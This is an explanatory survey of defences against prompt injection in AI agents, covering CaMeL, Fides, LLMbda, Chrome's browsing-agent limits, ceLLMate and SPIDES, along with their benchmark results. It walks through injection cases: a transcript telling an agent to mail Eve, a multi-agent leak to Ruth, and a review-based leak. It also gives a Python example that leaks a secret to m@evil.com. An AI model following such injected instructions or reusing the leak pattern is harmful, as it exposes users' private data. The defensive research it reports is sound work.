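A user asks an agent to summarise Tuesday's meeting and mail the notes to Alice. The transcript is confidential, and only the user, Alice and Bob may read it. It includes a supplier's message that Bob pasted into the meeting chat. The message contains a hidden instruction to send the transcript to eve@example.com.

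In CaMeL, the planner receives the user's request and the descriptions of the tools, and writes a program in Python. Simplified, it might be:

```python
transcript = get_transcript("Tuesday")
notes = ask_quarantined_model("Summarise this meeting", transcript)
send_email(to="alice@example.com", body=notes)
```

An interpreter then runs the program. It records where each value came from, and before every tool call it checks the arguments against a policy. The values in this program would have these labels:

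| Value | Source | Who may read it | Trusted? |
|---|---|---|---|
| "Tuesday" and Alice's address | The user's request | Anyone | Yes |
| transcript | The transcript tool | The user, Alice and Bob | No |
| notes | The transcript and the planner's question | The user, Alice and Bob | No |

The first line only reads data for the user, so the interpreter allows it. On the second line, the quarantined model reads the hidden instruction and may try to follow it, but it has no email tool. For the third line, a sensible policy would forbid sending private data to anyone not allowed to read it. Alice is allowed to read the notes, so the email goes out.

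The instruction to write to Eve has no effect because the planner finished the program before the system fetched the transcript. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) calls this property control-flow integrity. Untrusted data can determine which existing branch of the program runs, but it can't add a new one.

The injection can still corrupt the data the program handles. If the user had asked the agent to mail the notes to "whoever is doing the follow-up", the program would have taken the address from the transcript, and the injection could have supplied Eve's. The program would then run exactly as written, and only the policy would stop the email, because Eve isn't allowed to read the transcript. Neither part of CaMeL prevents the injection from making the notes false or empty.

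### Labels and hidden variables in Fides

The planner in Fides chooses one tool call at a time, like an ordinary agent, rather than writing a whole program in advance. Fides controls what information the planner receives between calls.

Each label has two parts. Integrity is either trusted ($T$) or untrusted ($U$). Confidentiality can be just public or secret, but a list of the people who may read the data is more useful. Combined data take the stricter label on both counts, which for lists of readers means that only people who may read both sources may read the result:

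$$(i_1, R_1) \sqcup (i_2, R_2) = (i_1 \sqcup i_2,\; R_1 \cap R_2), \qquad T \sqcup U = U.$$

These labels form a lattice, which means any two labels have one least strict label that is at least as strict as both. With only public and secret data, there are four labels, from trusted and public at the bottom to untrusted and secret at the top. Data can move up the lattice, but it can move down only through a permitted exception.

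Fides labels a model's answer as if the model had used everything in its input, since it can't determine which parts the model relied on. The conversation with the planner therefore has a label too. When a tool result has a stricter label than the conversation, Fides stores the result in a variable and gives the planner only the variable's name, so the conversation keeps its current label. The planner can pass the variable to a tool, ask the quarantined model about its contents, or open it, which gives the conversation the stricter label.

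The meeting request would go as follows, where $M$ stands for the user, Alice and Bob:

| Step | Label of the data | What Fides does |
|---|---|---|
| The user's request arrives | Trusted, anyone | Adds it to the conversation |
| The planner requests the transcript | Trusted, anyone | Allows the call, which only reads data |
| The tool returns the transcript | Untrusted, $M$ | Hides it in variable #1 |
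| The planner asks the quarantined model to summarise #1 | Untrusted, $M$ | Hides the answer in variable #2 |
| The planner mails #2 to Alice | Untrusted, $M$ | Allows the call, because Alice is in $M$ |

The conversation's label stays at "trusted, anyone" throughout, because the planner never sees the transcript or the notes.

For email, Fides has a rule with two alternatives. If $A$ is the set of recipients and $R$ the set of people who may read the message's contents, the call goes ahead if

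$$A \subseteq R \quad \text{or} \quad \text{the decision to send is trusted.}$$

The table shows how this rule would treat other emails containing the notes:

| Email | Has the planner opened the transcript? | May the recipient read the notes? | Is the decision trusted? | Result |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| To Alice, as the user asked | No | Yes | Yes | Allowed |
| To Carol, who missed the meeting, as the user asked | No | No | Yes | Allowed |
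| To Alice, as the user asked | Yes | Yes | No | Allowed |
| To Bob, as an injection asked | Yes | Yes | No | Allowed |
| To Eve, as an injection asked | Yes | No | No | Refused |

The email to Bob is unwanted, but it contains nothing he couldn't already read. The email to Carol is declassification, because it releases confidential data to someone outside the list of readers. Fides allows it on the assumption that a decision based only on trusted text reflects what the user wanted.

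In their tests, Costa and colleagues also blocked messages containing untrusted links unless the decision to send was trusted, since a link can carry data to an attacker's website. But the tested rule didn't check the arguments' labels. A planner could ask the quarantined model who should receive the notes, leave the answer hidden, and mail the notes to that address. The decision to send would count as trusted even if the address was Eve's. Requiring the recipient to be trusted too, as the paper suggests elsewhere, would prevent this.

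### Letting the planner see one bit

Some tasks depend on what the data contain. In one of Costa and colleagues' examples, the user wants the agent to check three emails for a meeting request and create a calendar event if it finds one. The planner has to know whether there is a request, but reading the emails would make its later decisions untrusted. Fides offers a way around this:

1. The planner asks the quarantined model whether the emails contain a meeting request, and specifies that the answer must be true or false.
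2. Fides forces the model's output into that format and labels it as an untrusted true-or-false value.
3. The planner opens the answer. A single true or false has no room for an injected instruction, so the policy can let the planner continue.
4. If the answer is true, the planner has the quarantined model extract the date and participants into another hidden variable, then passes that variable to the calendar tool.

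This is a form of endorsement, because untrusted data influence a protected decision. CaMeL can do the same task with an "if" statement in its program. It has more trouble with a request such as "do everything on my to-do list", because the planner can't write the program without first reading the list.

### Attacks stopped and tasks lost

Costa and colleagues tested Fides on AgentDojo, using GPT-4o and injections written for an attacker who knew which tools the agent had. Against an ordinary agent, 152 attacks succeeded. Hiding untrusted data without checking any policy reduced the number to 21, since the planner could still open a variable and follow the instructions inside. When Fides also checked its policies, no attack succeeded.

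Fides's result of zero successful attacks depends partly on how the researchers set up and scored the test. They marked a data field as untrusted if any of the benchmark's attacks used it, so the labels always covered the attacks. They also rejected three cases that AgentDojo had scored as successful attacks, for reasons such as AgentDojo counting a call that the policy had blocked. Their definition of an attack also excludes injections that only change what the agent says, for example by making it praise a hotel.

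The policies also prevented some legitimate tasks. These are the percentages of tasks completed without attacks, using OpenAI's o1, a reasoning model from 2024:

| | Office work | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, no policies | 70.0% | 82.0% | 96.2% | 87.6% |
| Labels and policies, nothing hidden | 48.0% | 75.0% | 37.5% | 17.1% |
| Fides | 64.5% | 68.0% | 56.2% | 54.3% |

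Hiding data recovered much of the loss, except in travel, where the policies already allowed most of the necessary calls. The largest remaining losses were in banking and Slack, where more than 40% of the tasks require the agent to look at data before it can decide what to do. In many banking tasks, the user asks the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, which is also what an attacker using prompt injection wants the agent to do.

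Each question to the quarantined model adds time and tokens, the units of text that AI companies charge for. Costa and colleagues didn't measure or optimise this overhead.

An independent test of CaMeL found an even larger loss. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, ran CaMeL three times on each of AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks. With policies on, the number of completed runs out of 48 fell from 32 to 18 with GPT-5.2 and from 34 to 18 with MiMo-v2.5. With so few tasks, the margin of error is over 20 percentage points either way, but completion also dropped in the runs under attack. Among the attacked runs that finished, GPT-5.2 completed 71% of the user's tasks without policies and 30% with them.

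In 97 of the same test's 144 combinations of a task and an attack, the attack needed an action that a normal program for the task wouldn't include, so the fixed program stops it by itself. In the other 47, the program could contain everything the attacker needed, so only a policy could reliably stop the attack.

Even among the 97, CaMeL without policies failed twice. The task was to read a file and follow its instructions precisely, so the planner wrote a loop with a branch for every tool. Because the program already included every tool, untrusted text could trigger any of them without adding an action. With policies on, CaMeL blocked every attack in the runs that finished.

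According to Garby and colleagues, CaMeL's developers recorded two successful attacks in their own tests. In one, the agent followed a tampered document's instructions when paying a bill, which the developers don't claim CaMeL can prevent. In the other, the agent quoted hotel reviews word for word, and AgentDojo wrongly counted the quotation as a successful attack.

### A leak through the branch that didn't run

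CaMeL's interpreter can also lose track of a secret. Garby and colleagues adapted an example from the 1970s, which works roughly like this:

```python
tmp = True
rich = True
if account.balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is above the threshold, the third line sets `tmp` to false and marks it secret. The fourth line then doesn't run, so `rich` stays true and CaMeL still treats it as public. The last line sends the email. If the balance is lower, `rich` becomes false and no email goes out. Whoever owns the address learns whether the customer is rich, although the program never sends the balance. CaMeL misses the leak because it updates a variable's label only when it runs a line that changes the variable.

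Garby and colleagues found two more gaps in CaMeL. When a program inserts an untrusted value into a longer piece of text, CaMeL can treat the result as trusted. CaMeL also retries failed programs in a loop that its labels don't cover. Whether the policy blocked an attempt can reveal one bit of a secret, so repeated attempts can reveal all of it.

The planner would have to write such a leak into the program, which is unlikely while the planner reads only trusted text. The gaps matter more if the planner makes a mistake or is hostile.

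By design, Fides restricts where data go but not what someone can infer from the agent's choices. If an agent emails Carol only when the transcript mentions redundancies, she can infer from the arrival of any email that they were mentioned. Costa and colleagues accept this because preventing it would rule out nearly every public action after the agent had read a secret.

LLMbda, a small programming language for agents, closes the gap more selectively. *Operationalizing CaMeL* had recommended replacing CaMeL's restricted Python with a language designed for security, and LLMbda is one. Every value in LLMbda carries a label, and so does the conversation with the model. A program can copy the conversation, have the model read a secret in the copy, and discard the copy, so the main conversation keeps its old label.

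The central theorem is about an observer who may see only some of the data. It compares two runs that differ only in data hidden from the observer. A model's answers vary, so each run has a probability distribution over what the observer sees, $\mu$ for one and $\nu$ for the other. The probabilities can add up to less than 1 because a run may never finish. The theorem guarantees that some $\omega$ exists with

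$$\mu \le \omega, \qquad \nu \le \omega \qquad \text{and} \qquad \sum_x \omega(x) \le 1.$$

Suppose that with one secret, the observer sees "yes" with probability 0.6 and the run otherwise never finishes. With another secret, the observer sees "yes" with probability 0.3 and "no" with probability 0.2. Taking the larger probability for each answer gives 0.6 + 0.2 = 0.8, so the condition holds, and the difference could come entirely from runs that didn't finish. If the second secret produced "no" with probability 0.7 instead, the total would be 1.3, which the theorem rules out because the answers themselves would reveal something about the secret.

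The proof covers every program in the language, including programs that a model writes while the agent is running. Lean, a computer proof checker, verified each step. The proof also applies to the interpreter that runs the agent, whereas CaMeL has no comparable theorem. A secret can still affect whether a run finishes, and the theorem doesn't show that the data is labelled correctly.

### Endorsements in the planner's program

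Garby and colleagues also built Randori, an agent written in LLMbda. Its planner first tests its program with imitation tools, so it can correct the program without touching real data. The program may include endorsements, each of which marks a particular untrusted value as trusted. The planner has to write these before the agent contacts the outside world.

On the banking tasks, Randori completed 36 of 48 runs with GPT-5.2 and 31 with MiMo-v2.5, with its policies on in every run. This is about as good as CaMeL without policies and well above CaMeL with them. Randori enforces only some of CaMeL's policies, which may explain part of the advantage.

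Attacks succeeded in two of 1,296 runs, both on the same task. The user had told the agent to follow the payment instructions in a file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. Without endorsements, Randori blocks this attack but completes fewer tasks (30 instead of 36 with Qwen3.7-plus, and 26 instead of 31 with MiMo-v2.5).

The proof shows that endorsements can't make secret data public, however many a program contains. They can still make the agent act on an attacker's data, as in the two successful attacks, and nothing forces the planner to use them sparingly.

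### When one agent instructs another

CaMeL's guarantee can fail when several agents work together. Peters-Gill and colleagues demonstrated this with three agents, each protected by CaMeL: one to coordinate, one to read a database and one to send messages. The user asked for a summary of job applicants' details to go to Julie on Slack. The database contained an instruction to email the details to ruth@email.com as well. The attack took four steps:

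1. The database agent returned the records. Its planner never saw them.
2. The coordinating agent had the quarantined model summarise the records. The injected instruction survived in the summary.
3. The coordinating agent's program put the summary into a sentence for the messaging agent, along the lines of "Send this summary to Julie".
4. The messaging agent treated the whole sentence as its user's request. Its planner read the injected instruction and wrote a program that also emailed Ruth.

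Each agent followed CaMeL's rules, but untrusted text became trusted when it passed from one agent to another. Peters-Gill and colleagues' solution, multi-CaMeL, splits every message between agents into an instruction and a set of variables. The receiving planner reads only the instruction. The interpreter ensures that text from a tool goes into the variables. The variables keep their labels, so the second agent can check them against the same policies as the first.

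The researchers tested five models on a version of AgentDojo that divides the tools among several agents. None of the agents had a data policy, so the results measure only the protection against added actions:

| Model | Attacks that succeeded without CaMeL | With CaMeL in each agent | With multi-CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% | 0.5% | 0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 0.4% | 0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1% | 0% | 0% |
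| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 0% | 0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0% | 0% | 0% |

Every attack that got past the separate CaMeL agents did so by passing from one agent to another. The newest models resisted nearly all of these attacks without help, but the attacks were fixed in advance. In a large public competition, attackers who could adapt found successful injections against every leading model tested.

On AssetOpsBench, a set of industrial maintenance tasks, CaMeL reduced the share of tasks completed by 21.6 percentage points on average, but by only 13.4 points for the two strongest models, Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. Multi-CaMeL reduced it by another 3.2 points on average, but by less than one point for those two. Stronger models therefore seem to lose less, even when no policies block their calls.

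Most failures happened because the planner had to commit to a program before seeing any results. In some, an agent couldn't find data for the requested dates and returned data for other dates instead, and the coordinating agent's program continued without adjusting for the change. Multi-CaMeL extends CaMeL's interpreter, so it can still miss a dependency like the one in the bank-balance example.

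### Endorsing a document instead of approving ten calls

When a policy blocks a call, the host can ask the user to approve it instead of refusing. Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026) argue in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* that the usual comparisons are therefore unfair to agents with labels, because tests typically allow these agents no help from a user but compare them with unprotected agents whose risky actions would need approval in practice. The researchers instead measured the share of tasks an agent could finish with at most $k$ user interruptions, and the total number of interruptions in the tasks it completed.

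Prudentia, an agent that extends Fides, gives its planner the labels and policies so that it can look for a plan that doesn't break them. The planner must justify opening a variable before it opens it. Prudentia can also ask the user to endorse a document instead of approving each call. For example, if an untrusted email contains a to-do list of ten items, the user could endorse the email once instead of approving ten actions.

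On AgentDojo, Prudentia completed up to 9% more tasks without interruptions than Fides did, and it reduced total interruptions by a factor of up to 1.9. On WASP, a benchmark of web tasks, it needed no interruptions. Even simple labels reduced interruptions by a factor of up to 1.5 compared with an ordinary agent, without reducing the number of completed tasks.

These tests used harmless tasks and assumed that the user would approve every request, which is reasonable for counting interruptions but doesn't show whether people can spot a bad document. A user who approves ten actions separately has a chance to notice an unwanted eleventh, but a single endorsement of an email also makes any instruction hidden in it trusted. Anthropic's paid testers approved most of the dangerous commands they saw, and a user who skims a long email may not do much better.

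Kolluri and colleagues left declassification out of Prudentia because whether someone may release private data usually depends on the recipient and the occasion. They prefer to ask the user about each call.

Other recent systems try to keep an agent working within the rules. Zhou and Zhang describe APPA, which checks proposed calls before they run. When APPA blocks a call, the agent can continue in an isolated branch and recover in ways the policy permits. GAAP keeps a record of what an agent has disclosed in earlier tasks, which a label on a single conversation can't capture. SafeFlow extends labels to messages and tool results across several agents, but a model assigns its risk labels, so they can be wrong in the same ways as any other judgement a model makes. Similar labels can apply to the parts of a web page.

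### Wrong labels and rightful exceptions

All these systems depend on the data being labeled correctly at the start. In Fides, the labels usually come from a wrapper, a piece of trusted code around each tool. For email, Costa and colleagues assumed that only the sender and the recipients may read a message. If somebody has shared the message more widely, this assumption makes the system too strict. If a wrapper wrongly marked the meeting transcript as readable by the whole company, Fides would let the agent email it to any employee, because every later check relies on that label.

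Coarse labels can also make an agent fail legitimate tasks. The tests treated the body of every email as untrusted, so the agent couldn't distinguish a genuine password-reset link from a fake one and failed a task that needed the real one. A wrapper could instead label each email based on the sender's verified address. Costa and colleagues also mention marking a document as trusted once an injection detector has cleared it, but an attacker who fools the detector would then get past the labels too.

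Labels can also become so strict that they allow almost nothing. If only the user, Alice and Bob may read Tuesday's transcript, and only the user and Carol may read Thursday's, then only the user may read notes the agent writes after reading both. The agent can't mail the notes to Alice without an exception, even if every sentence in them comes from Tuesday's transcript. Tools that identify which inputs affected an answer could give it a less strict label, but they rely on an estimate of which inputs the model used.

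Short answers are a limited exception. An answer chosen from $n$ options carries at most $\log_2 n$ bits, so one true-or-false answer carries one bit, but ten of them can distinguish 1,024 cases. Costa and colleagues left forced answer formats out of their benchmark tests, so the results don't show how safe those formats are. Even a single bit can be too much. If the planner asks whether the group agreed to publish the transcript, the supplier's message could make the quarantined model answer "true".

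Zhou and Zhang propose recording which decisions each source may influence. The transcript could then supply facts for the notes but could not be used to authorise its own release.

The systems differ in who makes exceptions. In Prudentia the user endorses documents, while in Randori the planner writes endorsements into its program. Fides allows the email to Carol because the user asked for it, which is reasonable if the transcript belongs to the user. If it belongs to the company, being allowed to read it doesn't entitle the user to share it with Carol. Costa and colleagues also describe a stricter rule, which requires the recipients to be on the list of readers and the decision to be trusted. In their tests, they applied it only to a tool that adds people to a calendar event. Applied to email, the rule would block the notes to Carol even if someone with authority over the transcript had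 added her to its readers. That person would also have to endorse the decision, or the planner would have to make the decision without opening untrusted data.

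## Chrome's limits on its browsing agent

Fides can label an email by its sender and recipients, but a web page doesn't come with a record of who wrote each paragraph or who may read it. A browser tracks which website each part of a page came from, and Google used this information to set limits on Chrome's browsing agent.

### One agent on many signed-in sites

Browsers use the same-origin policy to separate websites. An origin is roughly one website, identified by the protocol, host name and port number in its address. A script from one origin can't read another origin's data, so a recipe site can't read the email open in the next tab. Users can still copy text from one page to another. The policy works because normally only a person moves data between sites this way.

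An agent moves data between sites automatically. It browses while signed in as the user, and what it reads on one site stays in its conversation when it opens the next. The second site can then include an instruction for the agent to paste in something from the first.

Wang, Chen and colleagues (2026) tested this on five browsing agents, not including Chrome's, in *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers*. Each agent first handled invented private data, such as bank or pharmacy details, and then visited a page with an injected instruction to post the data there. OpenAI's ChatGPT Atlas posted the data in 99 of 150 runs. In a test without an attacker, the researchers embedded a private page inside another site's page and asked for a summary in a text box. The open-source browser BrowserOS copied private data into the box every time. It leaked nothing when the two pages were separate and neither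 contained an injection.

### Agent Origin Sets and a recipe

*Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) describes Agent Origin Sets, Google's design for limiting the agent's access to sites. Under this design, Chrome keeps two lists for each task, one of sites the agent may only read and one of sites where it may also click and type. A gating function determines which sites go on the lists.

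For example, a user has a lasagne recipe open and asks Gemini, Google's AI model, to buy the ingredients from a certain online supermarket. The user is also signed in to an email account and a bank. In the full design, the task would go like this:

1. Gemini shows its plan, and the user starts the task.
2. Gemini's planner proposes reading the recipe site and acting on the supermarket's site. The gating function checks that both are relevant. It sees no web content, so text on a page can't persuade it directly.
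3. Chrome gives the planner the recipe page without the advertisements, which other sites supply in separate frames.
4. The planner opens the supermarket's site and fills the basket.
5. At the checkout, Chrome asks the user to complete the purchase.

The planner receives only part of what the user can see:

| Content | Does the planner receive it? |
|---|---|
| The recipe | Yes |
| Readers' comments hosted by the recipe site | Yes |
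| An advertisement in another site's frame | No |
| The user's email and bank pages | No, as the task doesn't need them |
| The supermarket's product pages and reviews | Yes |
| The supermarket password | No, Google Password Manager fills it in |

A comment under the recipe can therefore still contain a prompt injection. Even if it tells the agent to send the user's address to an unknown site, the planner can't open that site without the gating function's approval. Chrome also limits model-written URLs to known, public ones. Otherwise the agent could leak the user's address by requesting a URL that contains it.

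Google's first version tracked only the sites the agent could act on. It had no separate list for sites the agent should read but not change, such as the recipe site.

### A critic that doesn't read the page

Besides the gating function, which checks sites, Chrome uses a second model called the User Alignment Critic. After the planner proposes an action, such as a click or text to type, the critic checks whether it serves the user's goal. The critic receives only metadata describing the action, not the raw page. If it rejects the action, it gives the planner feedback for a new plan. After repeated failures, the planner can return control to the user.

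Google names CaMeL as a partial inspiration, but Chrome's planner reads untrusted pages before choosing actions, which CaMeL's planner never does. The critic is closer to Claude Code's classifier, which also checks actions without reading the tool results that may have prompted them.

Here too, limited information can keep the critic from detecting a bad action. If an injected comment made the planner add an expensive bottle of truffle oil, the critic might register only another grocery item going into the basket. It would need the recipe to identify truffle oil as unnecessary for lasagne, and the recipe is web content.

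### When Chrome asks the user

Google's *Ask Gemini in Chrome to complete tasks for you with auto browse* lists when the user may have to step in during auto browse, Google's name for the agent's multi-step tasks. Gemini may ask the user to take over to finish a payment, accept terms of service or create an account. It aims to ask for confirmation before it starts a task, sends a message, changes the user's data, submits a form or opens a site with highly sensitive financial or health data. It also needs permission to sign in with the password manager.

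Google's descriptions of these checks differ in strength. Berschadski (2026), in *Future Mode Part 2*, tells businesses that Chrome requires a person's approval before any high-stakes action. The help page uses "may" and "aims to", and warns that Gemini could complete a purchase without permission. Parker likewise writes that the agent "will try to pause" before such actions. The weaker wording is safer to rely on, because a model helps recognise which actions are sensitive.

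### Fixed rules and model judgements

In guidance for developers of other browsing agents, Google (2026) separates guardrails that always give the same result from those that depend on a model. Chrome uses both:

| Ordinary code enforces | A model judges |
|---|---|
| Which content reaches the planner, once the lists exist | Whether a new site is relevant to the task |
| Where the agent may click and type | Whether an action serves the user's goal |
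| Which model-written addresses it may open | Whether a page contains a prompt injection |
| Confirmation for sites on a fixed sensitive list | Whether some other actions need confirmation |

The first row depends on both columns. Code can reliably keep the agent to its list of sites, but a variant of the critic decides whether a new site belongs on the list. If it wrongly adds a site, the code will allow the agent to access it. The critic is harder to attack because it is isolated from web content, but it can still make mistakes.

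### What Google has released

Google launched auto browse on 28 January 2026 (Bloomberg, *Google Chrome's AI Agent Can Now Browse Web on Behalf of Users*, 2026). 9to5Google (2026) reported at the time that the agent's actions run in the browser on the user's device, while the model runs in the cloud. *Q1 2026 Summary from Chrome Security* (Bawa, 2026) reports that by April the security team was adjusting the defences based on real use and had built more sets of attacks to test them.

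Access has widened since then. In July, Google let Gemini Spark, another of its agents, use Chrome's signed-in accounts with the user's permission, as Sood (2026), in *Gemini Spark now works with Chrome*, reported. In October, auto browse reached subscribers in India on computers and Android phones, according to Kanchwala, in *Gemini Can Now Browse For You, But Should You Let It?*

Berschadski confirmed in August that auto browse uses the critic and that Google was limiting the agent to sites relevant to its task. Chrome also marks the agent's page visits in the browsing history, so the user can check where it went. Neither Berschadski nor the help page mentions a separate read-only list, so it is unclear whether Google has added one since the first version.

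None of these documents gives a success rate for attacks on Chrome's agent, with or without the new defences. Google measures this rate internally by running automated attacks on test sites, but without published results, nobody outside the company can tell how well the design works. Google also offers up to $20,000 for a demonstrated breach of the agent's security boundaries, and warns on the help page that the safeguards "do not guarantee protection against all risks".

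### From a readable site to a writable one

Even if every part works as intended, Agent Origin Sets leave one route for a leak. Let $A$ be the sites the agent may read and $W \subseteq A$ the sites it may act on. The design allows data to move from site $a$ to site $b$ whenever

$$a \in A \quad \text{and} \quad b \in W.$$

The lasagne task needs this, since the agent has to take the ingredient names to the supermarket's site. But the user might also ask it to check their email for what the guests can't eat. The email site is then added to $A$, and the supermarket is already in $W$. An instruction injected into a product review could cause the agent to paste a private email into a new public review. The lists would allow this, because they restrict which sites can receive data but not which data they receive.

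The critic might veto the review, or Chrome might ask the user before posting it. Both safeguards depend on the critic or the user recognising the problem. The agent can also get private data without visiting a website. According to the help page, Gemini may use information from connected apps such as Google Workspace and share it with the sites it uses for the task.

A leak can also happen within a single site. The supermarket's site contains both the user's home address and public reviews, so limiting which sites the agent can access can't stop it from posting the address in a review.

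### Rules on web requests in ceLLMate

In *ceLLMate*, Meng, Feng and colleagues (2025) call Google's two levels of access coarse. Their own system can give an agent access to a site's basket but not its reviews. It checks HTTP requests, the messages a browser sends to a website's server, because these have more definite meanings than clicks. A rule about clicks would be hard to write, since a click at the same position might open an email or delete it.

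A website's developers publish an "agent sitemap" that lists these requests and what each one does. In the paper's Amazon example, one request views the basket, another changes it and a third places an order. Developers or other trusted parties also write rules, such as one that allows an order only up to a chosen amount. A model selects the rules the task needs based only on what the user asked for, and the user confirms them. A browser extension then checks each request.

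With a $50 limit, for instance, the extension reads the total from Amazon's checkout page and blocks any order above that amount. The agent could still place two $49 orders, so ceLLMate can also count orders and allow only one. If the user doesn't name a website, ceLLMate grants no access.

The researchers tested rule selection on 209 shopping, travel and software-development tasks. Three models chose exactly the right rules in 94% to 100% of tasks, depending on the model and the type of task. They filled in limits and other details less reliably, getting them all right in 81% to 97% of the 32 relevant shopping tasks. One model confused a wish list with a shopping basket.

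The researchers tested enforcement with 12 scripts that behaved like a fully hijacked agent on GitLab, a site for software projects. The agent had permission only to read and write issues, which are public discussions of problems. The scripts tried to delete projects, steal access tokens and add an attacker's login key, and ceLLMate blocked all 12. Every attack required an action the agent had no permission for, so the test shows that the filter works but not how many real attacks it would stop. The checks slowed a series of page visits by 7.25% to 15%, depending on the length of the sitemap.

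In the lasagne task, ceLLMate could let the agent fill the basket but stop it from posting a review. It doesn't track where data came from, so if the rules allowed a delivery note, the agent could put a private email in the note. It also doesn't check WebSockets, a separate connection type that many sites use for live updates. And it depends on sitemaps that websites would have to write and maintain. The researchers wrote the one for GitLab themselves.

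### Labels on page elements in SPIDES

*SPIDES* (Zverev, Kim and colleagues, 2026) applies labels like those in Fides to the parts of a page. The user keeps a list of trusted websites, whose operators mark each part as trusted or untrusted and specify which sites may receive it. On a shop's page, the agent would see the product's name, but SPIDES would hide a customer's review and the user's saved card number in variables, as Fides does.

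SPIDES treats clicks and form submissions on trusted sites as consequential, because the user may have an account there. They need the user's approval if untrusted data has influenced the agent or is part of the call. Typing without submitting is less risky, so SPIDES allows it if the decision and the data are both trusted, or if

$$s \in R_{\text{context}} \cap R_{\text{argument}},$$

where $s$ is the site receiving the text, $R_{\text{context}}$ is the set of sites allowed to receive everything the agent has seen, and $R_{\text{argument}}$ is the same for any hidden values in the text. In the supermarket example, a correctly labelled email would be untrusted, and the supermarket wouldn't be among its permitted recipients. SPIDES would therefore ask the user before the agent typed any of it into the supermarket's page.

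The researchers built 28 linked websites with 56 ordinary tasks and 56 attacks. They assumed a worst case in which an attacker controls a model's output once the model has read the attacker's text. No attack succeeded against SPIDES with any of five models. Between 53.2% and 73.2% of attacks succeeded against SOPGuard, Wang and colleagues' defence, which asks the user before data moves to a different site.

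Two cases account for much of the difference. In the first, a private message on a social network contained an instruction for the agent to copy the user's recovery email address into their public profile. SOPGuard allowed this in all 25 runs because the data stayed on one site. SPIDES, which hides untrusted text such as the message, prevented the disclosure in all 25. If an agent had read the message, SPIDES's rules would have let it type the address but blocked the click on "Save changes". In the second case, the user wanted to check a discount on one site against the normal price on another. SOPGuard interrupted all 25 runs of this harmless task, while SPIDES needed no approval in 21.

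The effect on ordinary tasks varied by model. These are the shares completed, combined from the paper's results for two kinds of task:

| Model | No defence | SPIDES |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 91% | 86% |
| GPT-5.6 Terra | 88% | 77% |
| Claude Opus 5.5 | 58% | 67% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 69% | 69% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 89% | 82% |

Claude Opus 5.5 did better with SPIDES, partly because SPIDES hid login details from the model. When the model could see them, Anthropic's safety filters sometimes blocked the task. A task cost an estimated $0.37 to $1.42 with SPIDES, about twice as much as without it.

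SPIDES required 1.84 approvals per completed task, and the researchers assumed that users would always recognise a harmful request. Real users, like Anthropic's testers, would probably approve some. The researchers also supplied correct labels for every page. On the real web, thousands of site operators would have to add labels and keep them accurate as their pages changed. Even correct labels identify recipients only by website, so they can't distinguish a private message to a friend from a public post on the same social network.
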